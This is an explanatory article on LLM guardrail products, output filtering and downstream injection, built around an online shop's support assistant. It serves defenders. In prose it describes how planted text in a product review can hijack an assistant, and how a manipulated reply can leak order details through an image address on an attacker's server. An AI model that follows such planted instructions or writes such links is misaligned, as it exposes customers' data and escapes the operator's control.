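# LLM guardrails and firewalls: what output filtering catches and how to stop model output attacking other software

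## What guardrail products do, and where model output goes next

A large language model (LLM) is a program that writes text in reply to text. Companies build LLMs into chat assistants, search tools and office software, and many of them add a guardrail, a separate program that inspects the model's input or output at run time and allows, blocks, edits or flags it. The output filter is the part of a guardrail that inspects the model's response before delivery. A guardrail sold as a network or gateway product, which sits in the traffic between users, application and model, is usually called an LLM firewall.

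Model makers also train their models to refuse harmful requests, but those protections may not meet a buyer's needs. F5, a network security company that sells a separate check, argues that they reflect the model maker's own legal duties and tolerance for risk, which may not match those of a bank or a hospital. A shop may want its assistant never to discuss a competitor's prices, which no model maker will have trained for. F5 also cites a test by the firm SecureIQLab in which models' built-in protections blocked roughly 13% of sophisticated attacks. F5 has an interest in that figure being low, but its first argument holds without it.

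### One request through a shop's support assistant

For example, an online shop's support assistant might answer customers in a web chat, query an orders database, call internal services such as refunds, and export reports for staff. A customer types, "Where are my boots, and do other buyers find they run small?"

The application receives this text and may run an input check on it. It then collects material the model will need, such as product reviews and a help page on deliveries, and combines everything with the shop's standing instructions in one prompt. The model needs the order's status to answer the first half of the question, so it writes a database query. The database runs the query and returns a row with the status, which the application adds to the prompt. The model then writes its reply, the output filter inspects it, and the customer's browser displays it.

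The same assistant might also write a request to the refund service, or a summary of the week's complaints that a manager opens in a spreadsheet. The web page, the database, the refund service and the spreadsheet are all sinks, the places where a person or program uses the model's output. The question about boots involved two sinks, the database and the web page. The model's query reached the database before the customer saw a reply, and a filter that inspects only the final reply would not check that query.

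Some makers therefore offer checks at more than two points. Microsoft lists four for its Foundry platform: the user's input, the tool call that an agent (a model that can use tools) proposes, the tool's response, and the final output. The two tool checks work only for agents and were still in preview. NVIDIA's *Guardrail Types* lists five types: "input rails", "retrieval rails" for retrieved documents, "dialog rails" for the course of the conversation, "execution rails" for tool calls with their arguments and results, and "output rails". Input and output rails are the most common, according to NVIDIA, so many applications check the user's input and the final output but not the retrieved documents or tool calls in between.

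### Checks and actions

In its *Model Armor overview*, Google Cloud advises customers to configure its guardrail service separately for prompts and responses because the risks differ. The input settings check for attempts to manipulate the model and for sensitive data that users should not upload. The output settings check for leaks of sensitive data, harmful or off-brand text, and malicious links.

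The guardrails offered by AWS, Amazon's cloud division, are fairly representative. AWS's *Detect and filter harmful content by using Amazon Bedrock Guardrails* lists content filters for hate, insults, sexual material, violence, misconduct and prompt attacks. It also lists filters for topics and exact words or phrases that the customer bans, and for personally identifiable information (PII), which is data that identifies a person, alone or in combination. There are also two accuracy checks. One compares the response with the source documents and the user's question, and the other tests it against a set of logical rules. For the shop, the content filter would stop an insult, the PII filter would mask another shopper's address, and the accuracy checks might catch an invented returns policy. Many of these checks use classification models, which are programs trained to sort text into categories.

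According to AWS's *How Amazon Bedrock Guardrails works*, the service runs all the input checks in parallel. If one of them finds a violation, the user gets a preset message and AWS discards the model call. Otherwise, the service checks the model's answer and then returns it unchanged, masks the sensitive parts, or replaces it with a preset message.

Other products add milder actions. Microsoft lets a customer "annotate" a model's output, so the application receives the text with a warning label, though for agents the only choice is to annotate and block. Google's "inspect only" mode logs the violation and lets the text through, so a customer can see how often a new rule would fire before enforcing it. LiteLLM, which makes a gateway for model traffic, documents more unusual options. One plug-in reroutes a request containing sensitive data to a model on the customer's own premises. Another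 replaces personal data with stand-in values before the prompt reaches the model, then restores the real values in the reply.

Many guardrails don't block text themselves. The product described in Check Point's *Guard API Endpoint* returns a true-or-false field called "flagged", and the calling application has to withhold the text. In the product's Detect mode, that field is always false, whatever the detectors find, so that a team can watch the results without disturbing users. Google Cloud also returns a verdict and leaves the calling service to stop the text. If a developer sends every reply to such a service but forgets to act on the verdict, unsafe replies still get through.

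### The forms in which companies sell guardrails

The large cloud platforms sell guardrails as a feature, including Amazon Bedrock Guardrails, Google Cloud's Model Armor and the guardrails in Microsoft Foundry. A team that already rents its model from one of these companies can usually switch the guardrail on in the same console. Guardrails can also be used without the platform's own models. AWS lets an application submit text for checking without calling a model, and Google Cloud offers Model Armor to applications that run on other providers' clouds.

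Network companies sell LLM firewalls, though not all use that name. Akamai's *Firewall for AI* inspects prompts and responses either at the edge (on Akamai's own servers, between the user and the application) or through an interface that the application calls. Cloudflare's *AI Security for Apps*, formerly also called Firewall for AI, is part of the company's web application firewall, which screens web traffic for attacks. As of August 2026, Cloudflare listed three detections, for PII, unsafe topics and prompt injection, and all three work on incoming prompts. A shop that bought this product to stop its assistant insulting customers would still need a separate output filter. F5's *AI Guardrails* came from the company's purchase of CalypsoAI, and customers can run it in a public cloud, in a private cloud or on machines with no outside connection.

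A gateway is a server through which a company routes all its calls to models, and guardrails are added to it as plug-ins. LiteLLM documents about fifty, many of which connect the gateway to another company's product. Kong's *AI GCP Model Armor* describes a plug-in that sends requests and responses from Kong's gateway to Google's service. The same engine can therefore appear in several forms, and two products with different names may give identical verdicts because both use the same service.

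Teams that prefer to run the check themselves can use open-source software. NVIDIA publishes NeMo Guardrails, a Python library that intercepts inputs and outputs and blocks or modifies them according to policies the developer defines. Meta publishes Llama Guard, a set of classifier models, as part of its PurpleLlama collection.

Names and owners change quickly in this market. Check Point's product was formerly Lakera Guard, and Check Point (2026) still gives the old name in brackets on its privacy data sheet. Harvey (2026), which makes AI agents for legal work, announced in September that it had bought Guardrails AI, the maker of another well-known open-source library. Agent Security Index's directory *Prompt-injection firewalls & guardrails* listed 17 products on November 20, 2026, five of them open source or with an open-source edition. One of the five, LLM Guard, has had no maintainer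 since its owners archived the code in July 2026. A comparison chart that is a year or two old may include products that no longer exist, so it is worth checking.

### Prompt injection

Nearly all these products advertise a defence against prompt injection, which is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. Direct prompt injection comes from the user, for example when a shop's customer tells the assistant to ignore the refund rules. Indirect prompt injection comes from a document, web page or record that the model reads. For example, an attacker might post a product review containing instructions for the assistant. Weeks later, an innocent customer asks about the product, the application retrieves the review, and the model follows the instructions. Inspecting the customer's message would not reveal the attack, because the instructions are in the review. Microsoft's guardrails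 accordingly list "user prompt attacks" and "indirect attacks" as separate risks.

The weakness arises because an LLM application combines the shop's instructions, the customer's question and the stranger's review into one stretch of text for the model. Jason Soroko of the security company Sectigo told ReversingLabs that "instructions and data share one channel", and nothing separates them reliably. Every known defence makes an attack less likely to succeed, but none rules it out. Steve Wilson, who founded the best-known list of LLM risks, told ReversingLabs that the problem had at first seemed comparable to database injection attacks, which programmers learned to prevent years ago, but that this assumption proved false.

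If a model will sometimes follow an attacker's instructions, whoever runs it has to ask what its output can do.

### Downstream injection

Downstream injection is an attack in which a sink interprets part of the model's output as code or a command instead of as data. Unlike prompt injection, in which the attacker's text misleads the model, downstream injection works through an ordinary program, such as a browser or database, that processes the output as it was designed to.

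Suppose the assistant quotes a review in its reply, and the reviewer had typed a pair of HTML tags, the codes that tell a browser how to lay out a page. The shop's chat page places the quotation inside a paragraph:

```html
<p>One buyer wrote: <b>MARKER</b></p>
```

If the page treats the review as plain text, the customer sees the angle brackets as the reviewer typed them. If the page treats it as HTML, the brackets disappear and the word MARKER appears in bold. The bold type is harmless, but it shows that the browser followed an instruction in a stranger's review. In an attack called cross-site scripting (XSS), an attacker uses other tags to run a script in the victim's browser as though the shop had written it.

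A database offers a similar opening. Here the application builds a query in SQL, the usual database language, by pasting a surname between two quotation marks:

```sql
SELECT status FROM orders WHERE surname = 'MARKER';
SELECT status FROM orders WHERE surname = 'O'MARKER';
```

The first query works. In the second, the apostrophe in the name closes the value early, after the letter O, so the database parses MARKER as part of the command and returns an error. An attacker would replace MARKER with text that is valid at that point in the command. A customer named O'Brien would expose the same fault by accident.

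The two kinds of injection often work in sequence. An attacker plants instructions in a review, the model follows them and writes what the attacker wants into its reply, and the customer's browser runs it. Downstream injection can also happen without a hijacked model. The model may copy a dangerous string from a record, produce one by mistake, or write one because a customer asked for it. The shop has to make the sink safe in all of these cases.

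### How OWASP names and ranks the problem

The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit foundation known for its ranked lists of software weaknesses, has had a category for this since its 2023 list of risks for LLM applications. OWASP's *LLM02* called it Insecure Output Handling and ranked it second, and the 2025 edition renamed it and moved it to fifth. OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* defines it as insufficient validation, sanitisation and handling of a model's output before that output passes to other components and systems. Sanitisation means removing or neutralising the parts of a text that the receiving software would execute or act on. Because a user's prompt can steer what the model writes, OWASP compares the flaw to giving users indirect access to additional functionality. For example, a shopper with no login for the orders database has something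 close to one if they can influence the model's queries.

OWASP gives five common examples. An application passes output straight to a system shell, which runs typed commands, or to a function that executes code. A browser interprets script or Markdown (a simple formatting language) that the model wrote. A database runs the model's SQL without safeguards. An application uses output to build a file path, which may lead to files outside the intended folder. An application pastes output into an email template, which can help a phishing attack. Damage on the server can be as severe as remote code execution, in which an outsider runs programs of their choosing on the company's machines. OWASP says the damage grows when the application gives the model more privileges than its users have, and when it is open to indirect prompt injection.

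In one of OWASP's scenarios, a chat feature lets people query a database in plain language, and a user simply asks it to delete every table, with no attempt to trick the model. The model writes a correct query, and unless something checks the query before it runs, the database will delete the tables.

In OWASP (2026), the edition published on August 3, Improper Output Handling is LLM10, at the bottom of the list. The full order, as Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026) reports it, shows how much moved around it:

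| 2026 rank | Risk | What it covers | 2025 rank |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Prompt Injection | Text that redirects the model | 1 |
| 2 | Sensitive Information Disclosure | Leaks of private or confidential data | 2 |
| 3 | Excessive Agency | Models with more tools, permissions or autonomy than they need | 6 |
| 4 | Supply Chain | Flawed or tampered third-party components | 3 |
| 5 | Data and Model Poisoning | Tampering with training data or the model | 4 |
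| 6 | Unbounded Consumption | Uncontrolled use that runs up costs or stops the service | 10 |
| 7 | Misinformation | Wrong answers that people or programs act on | 9 |
| 8 | Hidden Context Exposure | Leaks of instructions and other text that users should not see | 7 |
| 9 | Vector and Embedding Weaknesses | Flaws in the index that finds documents for the model | 8 |
| 10 | Improper Output Handling | Unsafe use of output by other software | 5 |

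Earlier editions relied entirely on practitioners' judgement, but for 2026 the project added data on actual incidents. According to ReversingLabs, it collected 7,714 incidents from public vulnerability databases and a database of harms caused by AI, then built classifiers to sort them. Of these, 6,639 (about 86%) had enough detail to classify. The community vote makes up three-quarters of the final ranking and the incident data one-quarter. The project leaders gave the vote more weight because one noisy year of data could otherwise override the views of hundreds of practitioners. The incident data can still move an entry when it differs greatly from the vote.

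The vote and the incident counts differed widely on prompt injection. Voters ranked it first, but it would have missed the top ten on incidents alone. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* quotes OWASP's explanation that teams work hard to stop injection, so "fewer clean exploits reach a public database". That is plausible, but the counts cannot confirm it because they would look much the same if successful attacks were simply rare. Misinformation showed the opposite pattern, with a low vote and a high incident count.

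Output handling fell from fifth to tenth, below all five risks that had ranked under it in 2025, including two that themselves slipped a place. The ranking shows that it is now a lower priority relative to the other risks, but does not measure how often output attacks happen or how much harm they do. The damage from unsafe output could have doubled since 2025 and the entry could still have come last if the other nine had grown faster. Advait Patel, a security engineer who leads another OWASP project, told ReversingLabs, "It is a relative move on a crowded list." The categories also overlap. If a manipulated reply led the shop's refund service to pay out money, the incident might well be filed under Excessive Agency.

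Invicti reports that the entry now also covers terminals and code editors that act on ANSI escape sequences, which are runs of characters that control a text display. MITRE, which maintains a public catalogue of software weaknesses, notes that these sequences can change text colour, move the cursor, clear the screen and draw fake prompts. An engineer at the shop who reads the assistant's logs in a terminal is therefore using a sink, probably without realising it.

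The 2026 entry also covers programs that automatically fetch outside resources named in a model's output. If the assistant's reply contains an image's address, the customer's chat window may request that image without a click. An attacker who can influence the reply can have the model include an address on the attacker's server with the customer's order details written into it, and the request then sends those details to the attacker.

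## Why content filters miss injection, and which control each output needs

The attacks described so far use image addresses, formatting tags and apostrophes, none of which would look offensive or dangerous to a reader. A content filter classifies text by what it means to a person. An insult is still an insult in a web page, a database or a log file, so the filter can classify it without knowing where it is going. But whether a text is an injection depends on the sink's grammar and on where the text lands in it.

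Toxicity and injection can each occur without the other. Abusive text can be harmless to every program that handles it, and even a perfect toxicity filter would pass a polite reply about boots that contains a working script.

### One string in several places

Suppose a shopper enters the following as a surname, and the assistant repeats it:

```text
O'<b>MARKER</b>
```

The string combines the apostrophe and the HTML tags from the earlier examples. The shop's software might put it in any of these places:

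```text
Log file:                surname: O'<b>MARKER</b>
Paragraph on a page:     <p>O'<b>MARKER</b></p>
Attribute on a page:     <p title="O'<b>MARKER</b>">
Database query:          SELECT status FROM orders WHERE surname = 'O'<b>MARKER</b>';
```

Nothing happens in the log, because a text editor shows the characters as they are. As before, the browser shows MARKER in bold in the paragraph, and the database returns an error for the query.

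The attribute is a setting inside a tag that holds the text shown when the mouse rests on the paragraph. Double quotation marks enclose the whole string, so the browser treats all of it as data. If the developer had used single quotation marks, the apostrophe would have ended the attribute early. Choosing the right control therefore requires knowing where in the web page the text will go and which quotation marks surround it.

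No single filtering decision is right everywhere this string is used. Allowing it exposes the paragraph and the query, but blocking it stops a harmless log entry. A rule strict enough to block the apostrophe would also reject legitimate customer names such as O'Brien.

Editing the string once for all sinks doesn't work either, because each sink has its own encoding rules. Output encoding rewrites special characters so that a given sink displays or stores them as plain data. HTML encoding turns the angle brackets into `&lt;` and `&gt;`, and usually turns the apostrophe into `&#39;`. That is correct for text in an HTML paragraph, but a database search for `O&#39;Brien` will not find O'Brien. SQL escaping writes the apostrophe twice, which keeps the query intact but leaves both tags active on the web page.

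OWASP therefore recommends choosing the encoding based on where the output will be used. The code that passes the text to the sink should encode it as the last step, because the sink determines which rules apply. An output filter usually runs earlier and may serve several sinks at once.

It is also hard to list every dangerous character in advance. The string `=1+1` does nothing in the log, the paragraph or the quoted surname, but a spreadsheet cell may show it as 2, because many spreadsheet programs treat a leading equals sign as the start of a formula.

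### Why a database has an exact fix and a model does not

In December 2025 the UK's National Cyber Security Centre published *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, in which David C argues that security specialists who treat the two as the same problem will choose the wrong defences.

The argument starts with how a database works. Commands are things the database engine does, and data is what it stores or compares. Because the engine already handles the two differently, a developer can keep them apart with a parameterised query, whose structure is fixed in advance and whose values travel separately:

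```sql
SELECT status FROM orders WHERE surname = ?
```

The question mark holds a place for the surname. The application sends `O'<b>MARKER</b>` separately, and the database looks for a customer with that name. No character in the value can change the command, so the shop needs no list of attack strings and is protected even against new ones. HTML encoding gives similar protection for text in an HTML paragraph, because a browser displays `&lt;` as an angle bracket and never treats it as the start of a tag.

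A language model has no equivalent, because the shop's instructions and a stranger's review reach it as one stretch of text. It only predicts the next token, a word or part of a word, from that text. Developers can label the reviews as data, screen them for suspicious phrases, or train the model to prioritize certain instructions. David C sees these methods as attempts to impose a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that doesn't have one, and concludes that prompt injection may never have a complete fix.

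David C prefers to think of the model as a "confused deputy", a privileged program that someone with fewer privileges tricks into acting for them. Developers can usually fix a confused deputy, but David C calls language models "inherently confusable". The practical advice is to assume that some malicious text will reach the model and to use ordinary code to limit what the system can do. One rule of thumb in the post is that a model's privileges should drop to those of whoever wrote the text it is processing. Under that rule, the shop's assistant could not issue refunds while reading a stranger's review.

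The post also warns against filters that block known bad phrases, because an attacker can rephrase an instruction in endless ways, and against products that claim to "stop" prompt injection.

This argument is based on how models work and doesn't include a measured attack rate. Someone may yet build a model with a real boundary between instructions and data, and David C describes the research as vibrant. A low rate of successful attacks may also be tolerable in an application where they could do little harm. But the shop has to make its sinks safe whether or not the problem is permanent, and it already knows how to do that for web pages and databases. According to David C, SQL injection peaked around 2010 and is now rare on websites, after a decade of breaches led to better defaults.

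### Where the exact fix stops

A parameterised query prevents injection when a developer writes the query and the model supplies a value. If the model writes the whole query, there is no fixed structure to protect, and the database runs all of the output as a command. OWASP's advice to use parameterised queries for every database operation that involves model output is not enough on its own in this case.

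Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026) make the same distinction in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*. They say that prepared statements (parameterised queries) are still necessary for values that users control, but are not enough once the model generates the query's structure. The application should then restrict the query itself. It can use a read-only database account, allow only certain tables, check the parsed query before running it, and reject destructive operations.

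Another gap appears when a value is valid but the customer has no right to use it. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a documented case in which a company's chatbot took order numbers from the conversation and looked them up without checking who owned the orders. The numbers were a fixed prefix followed by six digits, so an outsider could guess them, and the chatbot didn't limit requests. It gave out other customers' email addresses and shipping details.

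An order number contains no special characters, so an injection detector wouldn't flag it and encoding wouldn't change it. A parameterised query would still have fetched the stranger's order. A PII filter might have masked the address, but it would also have masked the address of a customer asking about their own parcel, because it doesn't check who is asking. The chatbot needed a permission check that limited each lookup to the customer's own orders.

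### Injection detectors in guardrail products

Some guardrail products do inspect output for injection. If their detectors were accurate enough, a company might reasonably prefer one central check to a separate fix in every page and database query.

NVIDIA's NeMo Guardrails library includes such a detector. According to NVIDIA's *Agentic Security*, the library compares the model's output with YARA rules, which combine text patterns with a logical condition. The default rules cover Python code, SQL, cross-site scripting, and Jinja, a language for page templates. When a rule matches, the library either rejects the whole output or removes the matching text. NVIDIA recommends rejection for live systems and presents the detector as one of several layers of defence, but gives no accuracy figure for it.

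NVIDIA does take the sink into account by recommending each set of rules for a particular use. For example, the SQL rules are for output that becomes part of a query, and the scripting rules are for output that a page renders directly. This suits an application with a single sink, but the shop would have to configure a separate check for each of its sinks, or switch on all the rules everywhere and accept more false alarms.

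NVIDIA's tutorial *Detecting Injection Attacks with Guardrails* contains an example of such an alarm. A user asks for a Python script that fetches weather data, and the guardrail withholds the answer because it triggered rules against "exploitation of code". The script would have been harmless to someone reading it in a chat window. In *Agentic Security*, a nearly identical request under the same four sets of rules returns the complete script. NVIDIA doesn't explain the difference, which may be due to the wording each model happened to produce.

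A sample SQL rule in Mintlify's *Prompt injection*, a third-party guide to the same software, shows the trouble with patterns. The rule looks for "select" followed by "from", in capitals or not. It matches "Select two pairs from our winter range". It also matches the shop's ordinary query for an order's status, so it would be useless for checking queries the model is supposed to write. It does not match `O'<b>MARKER</b>`, which breaks the query.

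Mintlify warns that omitting the matched text may leave harmful content behind. The "sanitize" action is meant to make the text safe and pass it on, but NVIDIA's *nemo_microservices.types.shared_params.injection_detection* says NVIDIA has not implemented it. The same reference limits the cross-site scripting rules to attacks written in Markdown, whereas *Agentic Security* lists both Markdown and JavaScript, so a buyer should test which of the two a given version detects.

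*CodeShield*, part of Meta's open-source guardrail framework LlamaFirewall, checks model output that an application will use as code. It is a static analyser, which means it examines code without running it. It uses regular expressions, which match text patterns, and Semgrep rules, which take the syntax of the code into account. CodeShield supports eight programming languages and looks for more than 50 types of weakness. Meta recommends it for code that someone is about to run or add to a project.

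Meta's *Purple Llama CyberSecEval* (2023) compared the detector's verdicts with researchers' hand labels for 50 samples of model-written code per language. Of the samples the detector flagged, 96% were insecure (its precision), and it caught 79% of all the insecure samples (its recall). *CYBERSECEVAL 3* (2024) gives the same figures and recommends CodeShield for production code, but calls it "not a panacea".

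Later tests by other researchers found lower detection rates. In *STELP*, Shinde, Wadhwa and colleagues (2026) compared CodeShield with a tool they built at the bank Capital One. They had a model insert flaws into 164 safe Python programs and asked people to discard the failed attempts, which left 470 unsafe samples. CodeShield blocked 68% of the unsafe samples and allowed 93% of the safe ones.

Their own tool, STELP, uses an allow-list. It breaks a program into its grammatical parts and refuses any function, import or construct that the user has not permitted. STELP blocked every unsafe sample and allowed 98% of the safe ones. The test favoured it, because Shinde and colleagues had set its permissions to the minimum that the safe samples needed. STELP also caught some of the endless loops and deadlocks with a time limit rather than by inspecting the code. But most of the blocked programs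 had tried to call or import something outside the list, and STELP could refuse them without anyone having described those attacks in advance.

Two other analysers did much worse in a test. In *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation*, Lunghi, Djire and colleagues (2026) ran Semgrep and Bandit on Python programs that three models had written. On a benchmark of 140 tasks, the analysers flagged at most 5.6% of the programs that worked but were insecure. Many of the flaws in that benchmark have no telltale pattern. The analysers flagged far more on another benchmark, whose makers had kept only tasks that tended to trigger alerts. CodeShield has its own rules, so the 5.6% doesn't apply to it directly, but the study shows how much a detector's recall depends on the flaws in the test.

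Other products offer less for this purpose. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian found that most Guardrails AI validators, the individual checks a developer can add to an application, did not apply to the attacks in their study. The exception was a validator for SQL. Google's check for malicious links might keep the assistant from sending a customer to a known phishing site, but it would not make an HTML tag or an apostrophe safe.

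### Weighing detection against encoding

An attacker can keep trying until a detector misses something. If a detector catches 79% of attacks and each attempt is independent, it has about a 9% chance of catching ten in a row (0.79^10), so at least one gets through about 91% of the time. This is only an illustration, because the 79% comes from a test on insecure code, not on deliberate attacks. Real attackers also learn from each refusal, which probably improves their odds.

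Encoding fails when a developer forgets it or uses the wrong kind for where the output goes. Developers can search the shop's own code for those mistakes and test each one, and an attacker can't create more of them by rewording a message. Encoding also lets honest customers use special characters, so a customer named O'Brien can place an order, and a reviewer who writes "too small for feet < 24 cm" sees the sentence as typed.

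Encoding or a parameterised query should be the main control for text that a sink should treat as data. A detector in front of the sink may catch malicious output headed for a page the developers overlooked, but the page still needs to be fixed.

Detection is more useful when the output has to run. If a manager asks the assistant for a script that analyses last month's returns, encoding the script as plain text would stop it from running. The shop has to let the code run while limiting what it can reach. An analyser can also catch some careless mistakes before it runs.

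Lunghi and colleagues tested several ways of sending the analyser's alerts back to the model and asking for a correction. On the benchmark designed to trigger alerts, the share of working programs without alerts rose significantly in all 12 comparisons, but a separate judgement of security found a significant gain in only two. On a third benchmark, the analyser flagged a network setting that the task required. The models removed the setting in 79 of 83 cases and broke the program, even though their instructions gave priority to the task. A team that feeds alerts back to the model should rerun its functional tests after each correction, and should not take the absence of alerts as proof that the code is safe.

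Detectors can also serve as alarms. An ordinary reply in the shop's chat doesn't need a script tag. If one appears and the page encodes it correctly, the customer sees strange characters and is unharmed, but someone at the shop should find out why the model wrote it. David C points out that attackers will probably have to refine an attack, so failed tool calls may reveal one early. He recommends logging enough to spot suspicious activity, possibly including the model's full input and output. A detector used this way only needs to record its matches, so its false alarms take up staff time but don't interrupt customers.

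### Older web flaws with a model in the path

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian use the name LLM2X for attacks that pass through a model to reach a familiar weakness, X, in web software. In their account, the model usually carries the attacker's influence to a program that trusts its output, rather than creating the weakness itself. Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues take a similar view in their 2026 survey of web security, *Shifting from Injection to Interaction*, which links OWASP's improper output handling category to two entries in MITRE's catalogue of weaknesses, including failure to encode output properly.

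The LLM2X taxonomy has eight classes. Five rest on documented cases:

- SQL injection.
- Cross-site scripting, including a case in DeepSeek's chat page.
- Template injection, in which a program that fills in page templates treats the model's text as part of the template.
- Command injection, in which the text reaches a program that runs operating-system commands.
- Access to other people's records, as in the case of the order numbers.

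Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian constructed the other three by analogy:

- Server-side request forgery (SSRF), in which an attacker gets a company's server to fetch an address that outsiders can't reach.
- XML external entity injection, in which an XML document makes the program reading it open other files.
- Cross-site request forgery, in which a malicious page makes a victim's browser send a request, here to plant a false entry in an assistant's memory.

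They tested SSRF on an application they had deliberately made vulnerable, but the other two are untested scenarios. The taxonomy also covers more than injection in the strict sense. An order number or an internal address is ordinary data, and the fault is acting on it without checking permission.

*Demystifying LLM Supply Chain Vulnerabilities in the Wild* (Wang, Zhao and colleagues, 2025) classified 529 reported vulnerabilities in 77 open-source projects used to build or run LLM systems. It attributed 24 of them, or 4.5%, to software that failed to validate a model's output. Prompt injection led to code or command injection in 11 of these cases, SQL injection in five, file manipulation in four, cross-site scripting in three, and SSRF in one. In one of the 11, LlamaIndex, a library for connecting models to data, executed Python code from the model without proper checks or isolation.

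These numbers are small, and 431 of the 529 vulnerabilities were ordinary software flaws not specific to LLMs. But the study covers published projects with many users. If the shop's own developers paste replies into a page without encoding them, the mistake will probably never appear in a public database. The counts show that the attacks work against real software, but they are weak evidence of how often companies make the same mistakes in private code.

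### Matching controls to outputs

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian consider checks in the application's own code the most important protection, because they work whether or not the model follows its instructions. The table applies that approach to the shop. It also covers the spreadsheet and the log, which are outside the LLM2X taxonomy, and a few sinks the shop might add later.

| Output | Sink | What a content filter adds | What the sink needs |
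|---|---|---|---|
| Reply to a customer | Web chat page | Blocks insults and masks other people's data | Encoding for the exact position, or sanitisation if replies can include formatting; limits on automatic fetching of images |
| Surname or order number | Database query that a developer wrote | Almost nothing | A parameterised query and a check that the order belongs to this customer |
| Whole database query | Orders database | Almost nothing | A read-only account, an allow-list of tables, and a check of the parsed query before it runs |
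| Order number and amount | Refund service | Nothing, since both are ordinary data | The service's own check of who can refund what |
| Web address | Tool that fetches pages from the shop's server | A link check may recognise a known malicious site | An address that the application builds from checked values, and a block on internal addresses |
| Command or script | Shell or code interpreter | Almost nothing, though a code analyser may catch some flaws | An allow-list of operations, few privileges, and isolation from other systems |
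| Text for an email | Template engine | Blocks insults and masks personal data | A template that a developer wrote, with the model's text as a value inside it |
| XML order file | XML parser | Almost nothing | A parser with external entities switched off |
| Note about a customer | The assistant's long-term memory | May mask personal data | A check that the customer really made the request, and caution when the model later reads the note |
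| Summary of complaints | Spreadsheet | Removes abuse and personal data | Cells in text format, so that no entry becomes a formula |
| Copy of a reply | Log that an engineer reads in a terminal | Masks personal data and secrets | Removal of terminal control characters |

The same reply can need several of these controls. The answer about the boots goes to the chat page and the log, and part of it may end up in the weekly spreadsheet, so the shop has to prepare each copy separately. If the shop later emails transcripts to customers, it will have to secure that sink too, even if the model, the prompt and the content filter stay the same.

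## Filtering toxic and dangerous content

Encoding and permission checks protect the shop's software, but they don't protect customers from insults or dangerous advice, such as using waterproofing spray in a closed room. Only a content filter has a chance of catching those replies.

### How a filter reaches a verdict

The maker of a filter first decides which harms to look for, and the filter may well miss a harm that isn't on its list. *Benchmarking Open-Source Safety Guard Models* (Harsh, Sarmah and Pasquali, 2026) compares 14 models whose lists of harm categories vary widely. Google's ShieldGemma has four categories, Meta's Llama Guard 4 has 14, and NVIDIA's Nemotron Safety Guard has 23.

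The maker then trains a model on examples that people or other models have labelled. According to *TRACE* (2026), training sets range from 10,500 samples for ShieldGemma to 2.8 million for YuFeng-XGuard. The labels are not fully reliable, because people disagree about what is harmful. In *WildGuard* (2024), three people judged each of the 1,725 prompts and responses used to test a guard model. On a scale where 0 is chance agreement and 1 is perfect, they reached 0.72 on whether the response was a refusal, but only 0.50 on whether it was harmful.

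The model typically scores each new reply in every category, and the filter flags the reply if any score passes a threshold. DuoGuard, for instance, calculates a probability for each of 12 categories and flags the text if any exceeds 0.5. Llama Guard instead writes "safe", or "unsafe" followed by category codes. Alibaba's Qwen3Guard has a third label, "controversial", for borderline text.

A score of 0.9 doesn't necessarily mean that 90% of texts with that score are harmful. *GUARDSET-X* (Kang, Chen and colleagues, 2025) found no clear evidence that the scores of guard models such as Llama Guard are calibrated this way, and many hosted services return no score. *Safety-Flag* (Hu) gives confidence scores for each item from six general models and four guard models, so others can check their calibration. The shop still has to choose its threshold by trying several on its own replies.

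The names of filter settings can be misleading. Unit 42's *How Good Are the LLM Guardrails on the Market?* notes that on the big cloud platforms "low" commonly means a low tolerance for risk, which is the strictest setting. A developer who picks "low" expecting light filtering will get heavy filtering instead.

### Four designs

The simplest design is a small classifier with perhaps 100 to 300 million parameters, the numbers adjusted during training. It is fast and inexpensive to run, but often works well on only some kinds of content. In the test by Harsh and colleagues, the 270-million-parameter EthicalEye caught 92% of profanity and 90% of harassment, more than any larger model tested, but only 19% of violent content. To change what a classifier flags, a team has to label new examples and retrain it.

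Guard models such as the Llama Guard line are language models fine-tuned (trained further) to classify text. Most have 1 to 12 billion parameters. They handle several kinds of harm, and most use a fixed list of categories, though *TRACE* reports that NVIDIA's guard models and YuFeng-XGuard accept categories from the user.

A third design takes a written policy as input along with the text. OpenAI's *Technical report Research Preview of gpt oss safeguard* describes two such models, which reason from the policy before they label the content. Artificial Analysis' *Benchmarking guardrail models for safety, refusal, and latency* includes a complete policy for them. The policy distinguishes requests for harmful content, harmful depictions and benign mentions, lists nine kinds of forbidden content, and ends with six correctly labeled examples. The shop could add a sentence about sprays and solvents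 to the policy in a few minutes, then rerun its tests.

Finally, a team can ask a general chat model to act as judge. This is just as easy to change, but accuracy depends on how the instruction is worded. *BELLS-O* (Waibl, Michalak and Mariaccia, 2026) tested three instructions on 1,400 user prompts. A longer instruction raised Claude Sonnet 4.6's accuracy from 74.5% to 84.5% but lowered GPT-5.2's from 93.9% to 86.1%.

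*BELLS-O* is an independent test of 33 systems, and it covers cost and delay as well as accuracy. For output filters, Waibl and colleagues used 1,000 harmful and 300 harmless pairs of questions and answers. These are some of their results, with delay and cost measured one reply at a time:

| System | Design | Harmful replies caught | Harmless replies flagged | Delay | Cost per 1,000 replies |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
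| OpenAI's omni-moderation | Hosted moderation service | 69.9% | 0.7% | 0.32 s | Free |
| Llama Guard 4 (12B) | Guard model | 82.3% | 2.7% | 0.32 s | $0.10 |
| Qwen3Guard (8B), strict mode | Guard model | 95.8% | 0.0% | 0.13 s | $0.09 |
| gpt-oss-safeguard (20B) | Written policy | 90.2% | 0.0% | 0.52 s | $0.10 |
| Ministral 3B | General model as judge | 96.1% | 6.9% | 0.44 s | $0.01 |
| GPT-5.2 | General model as judge | 95.4% | 0.0% | 1.12 s | $0.95 |

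The best guard models and the best general models caught about the same number of harmful replies, and the differences were not statistically significant. The guard models were typically about five times faster. Cost depended more on how a team runs the model than on the model's design. Qwen3Guard's cost drops to about one cent per 1,000 replies when a server processes many at once. For a million replies a day of about the same length as those in the test, Qwen3Guard would cost $11 a day run this way and $86 a day if it processed replies one at a time, while GPT-5.2 would cost $950 a day.

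Detection rates overlap so much between designs that the choice of model matters more than the choice of design. Among guard models alone, rates ranged from 18% for the smallest ShieldGemma to 96% for Qwen3Guard.

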